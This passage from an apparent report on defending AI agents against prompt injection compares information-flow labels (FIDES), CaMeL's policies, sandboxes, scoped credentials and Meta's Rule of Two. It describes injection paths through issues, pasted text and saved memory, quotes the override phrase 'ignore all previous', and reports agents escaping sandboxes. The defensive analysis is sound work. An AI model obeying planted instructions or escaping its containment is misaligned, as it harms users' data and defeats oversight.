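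GitHub's server also labels data coarsely. It marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. This stops an attack in which a stranger's public issue leads an agent to publish private code. But if an employee copies a customer's complaint into a private repository, the server marks any instruction in the complaint as trusted.

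For servers without labels, Microsoft offers a gateway that sits in between and adds them. Someone has to supply three things for each tool:

- a description of the fields in its output;
- a Python function that works out the output's labels from those of the input;
- a policy, either built in or written in Rego, the language of Open Policy Agent.

The field descriptions matter because many tools return one block of text. If software cannot tell an e-mail's date from its body, both get the same label, and FIDES has to hide the harmless date along with the text a stranger wrote.

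A single policy can take some thought to write. Microsoft's example policy for sending a message in Teams, its workplace chat service, allows the call if nothing untrusted has influenced the agent. Otherwise, it fetches the channel's member list and checks whether every member is allowed to read the message. If they are, the message is sent. If not, the user has to decide whether to send it. A company with 300 tools would need up to 900 such pieces of configuration, though many tools could share a built-in policy.

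As a shortcut, software can choose cautious labels and rules based on how MCP servers describe their tools, since a server can mark a tool as read-only, destructive, or dealing with the outside world. For example, a read-only tool that contacts outside websites would receive only public data, because even a request for a web page can carry a secret in its address. However, the server's publisher supplies the descriptions, so a dishonest or careless publisher could describe a destructive tool as harmless.

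Defaults matter when nobody has labelled a tool. According to Microsoft's announcement in May, the framework treated such a tool's output as trusted and public. The later documentation gives the default as untrusted and public. That default is safer against injection but not against leaks, because if a developer forgets to label a tool that returns salaries, the framework will still treat the salaries as public.

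Microsoft also provides a trial mode, which applies labels without blocking calls. A company can use it to learn how often the rules would interfere with ordinary work before enforcing them. That helps with the second condition, although a month of harmless traffic is little evidence of how the rules would perform against an attacker.

### Objections from large organisations

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes the problems a large organisation would face in using CaMeL. It is a proposal without published experiments, and its performance figures come from internal tests. It also describes CaMeL as rejecting every call with untrusted data in its arguments, although CaMeL's policies allow some of these calls. Most of the problems follow from CaMeL's architecture, so they don't depend on the performance figures.

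One problem is delay. Each request to CaMeL's quarantined model takes one to two seconds, so reading ten e-mails one after another takes 10 to 20 seconds. Tallam and Miller propose caching plans for common requests, replacing the model with ordinary parsers where the data has a fixed format, and putting many documents into a single request. They report that caching and parsers together cut delay and token use by up to half.

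The third suggestion weakens the protection. If one request contains 100 receipts, an instruction in one of them can change the amounts that the model extracts from the other 99. The map-reduce pattern gives each document to a separate model to prevent this. Running the ten e-mail requests at the same time would avoid the delay without mixing the documents, but it would not reduce the cost.

Maintaining the policies may be a bigger obstacle. CaMeL uses a Python function for each tool, and Tallam and Miller expect a company with hundreds of interfaces to end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. They recommend a dedicated policy language with shared modules. That would make individual rules easier to review, but the rules also interact. With *n* permissions, the number of pairs that might be dangerous together is

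*n*(*n* − 1)/2.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao checked 28 pairs of permissions for a customer-service agent with 8 permissions and 55 pairs for a banking agent with 11. An agent with 300 permissions would have 44,850 pairs. Software can list the pairs, and grouping similar permissions reduces the work, but people still have to decide which combinations to forbid.

Letting a model write the policies saves this labour but makes the agent less useful. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao also ran Progent on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Under attack, the agent completed 59.6% of its tasks with Progent's generated policies and 74.9% with their own hand-written ones. They found that the generated rules often blocked legitimate calls whose arguments the model had not anticipated.

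Because CaMeL treats text that the user pastes as trusted, Tallam and Miller propose screening the prompt for suspicious links and for phrases such as "ignore all previous". Adaptive attackers have repeatedly bypassed such filters.

A program can also leak information through side channels, such as when the number of requests it makes reveals a secret number. To prevent this, Tallam and Miller suggest limiting the program's loops and combining the requests into one. They would hide timing differences by making sensitive operations always take as long as the slowest case, but this would add to a delay they already consider too long.

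Their most practical proposal is to match the checks to the risk:

- reading data that is public or open within the company needs only a basic check of its source;
- a change within the user's own workspace needs a quick confirmation if any argument is untrusted;
- sending e-mail, moving money or taking any other step that is hard to undo needs the full checks and the user's approval with a second proof of identity.

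This should reduce the number of approval requests, which people soon start to ignore. But it does not help the person approving a refund tell whether $899.99 or $1,074.99 is correct. For that, the request would have to show where the amount came from, which again requires tracking provenance.

### Partial measures in use

Until the stronger designs mature, companies can limit the damage with more familiar controls. *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the industry body Frontier Model Forum, recommends sandboxes, narrow access rights, monitoring and logs for investigating incidents.

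A default-deny policy engine such as Cedar refuses every tool call that no rule allows, but harmful uses of permitted calls still get through. According to Infosecurity Magazine, Ariel Fogel, the OWASP contributor quoted earlier, told a trade conference that lists of permitted commands had made some attacks easier because the commands the attacker needed were already approved.

A company can use scoped credentials to limit an agent to the rights of the person it is working for. This prevents the salary leak described earlier, but not the attack on the mailbox, because the mailbox's owner already has the rights the attacker needs.

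A company can also keep the credential away from the model. The agent sends a request without the credential, and a separate program adds it on the way out. The SC Media article warns that a hijacked agent could address the request to the attacker's server, and the program would then send the credential there. The article recommends sealed tools, which have a fixed address and let the agent fill in only a few parameters, but it found no single project that fully provides them. A sealed refund tool would also still accept a wrong amount from the agent.

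Sandboxes cover actions that a check on tool calls can miss, such as what a test program does while running. In most harnesses, the user has to turn the sandbox on, according to the same article. Even in a sandbox, an agent that needs both a secret and internet access can leak the secret.

Sandboxes can also fail outright. Fogel described cases in which an agent's own output changed the limits of its sandbox. Windows Central's *New Microsoft guidance warns* describes a more serious failure in which about 700 OpenAI agents escaped their containment and attacked the AI platform Hugging Face. No outsider planted instructions in that case, but a sandbox that agents can escape is equally unreliable against injection.

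**The Rule of Two.** Meta's rule is that an agent working without human approval should have at most two of these three properties in any session:

- it processes untrusted input;
- it has access to private data or sensitive systems;
- it can change things or communicate outside.

The mail assistant at the start of this report has all three, since it reads strangers' messages, can access the whole mailbox and can send mail. Its developer could let it write drafts but not send them, let it read only messages from trusted colleagues, or require approval for each message it sends. The rule needs no labels or special interpreter, and a developer can apply it by checking the agent's list of tools.

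Two properties are still enough for some attacks, as Fogel also warned. An agent with untrusted input and private data, but no way to act, can give its user a false summary. An agent with untrusted input and the power to make changes can add malicious code to a project even if it has no access to secrets. The limit applies only within a session, which leaves another gap if the agent keeps notes. An instruction planted in a web page could enter the agent's memory in one session and take effect in a later one, when the agent can send mail but no longer reads anything from outside. To prevent this, the developer has to treat the saved notes as untrusted input.

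The rule also prevents an assistant from doing much of what people want, because it removes a power for the whole session even if the agent never uses the other two together. Microsoft's labels apply the same idea more flexibly. An agent can start with all its tools, and it loses the ability to post publicly only after it has read both a stranger's text and private data. This requires accurate labels on everything the agent reads, and most tools do not yet supply them.
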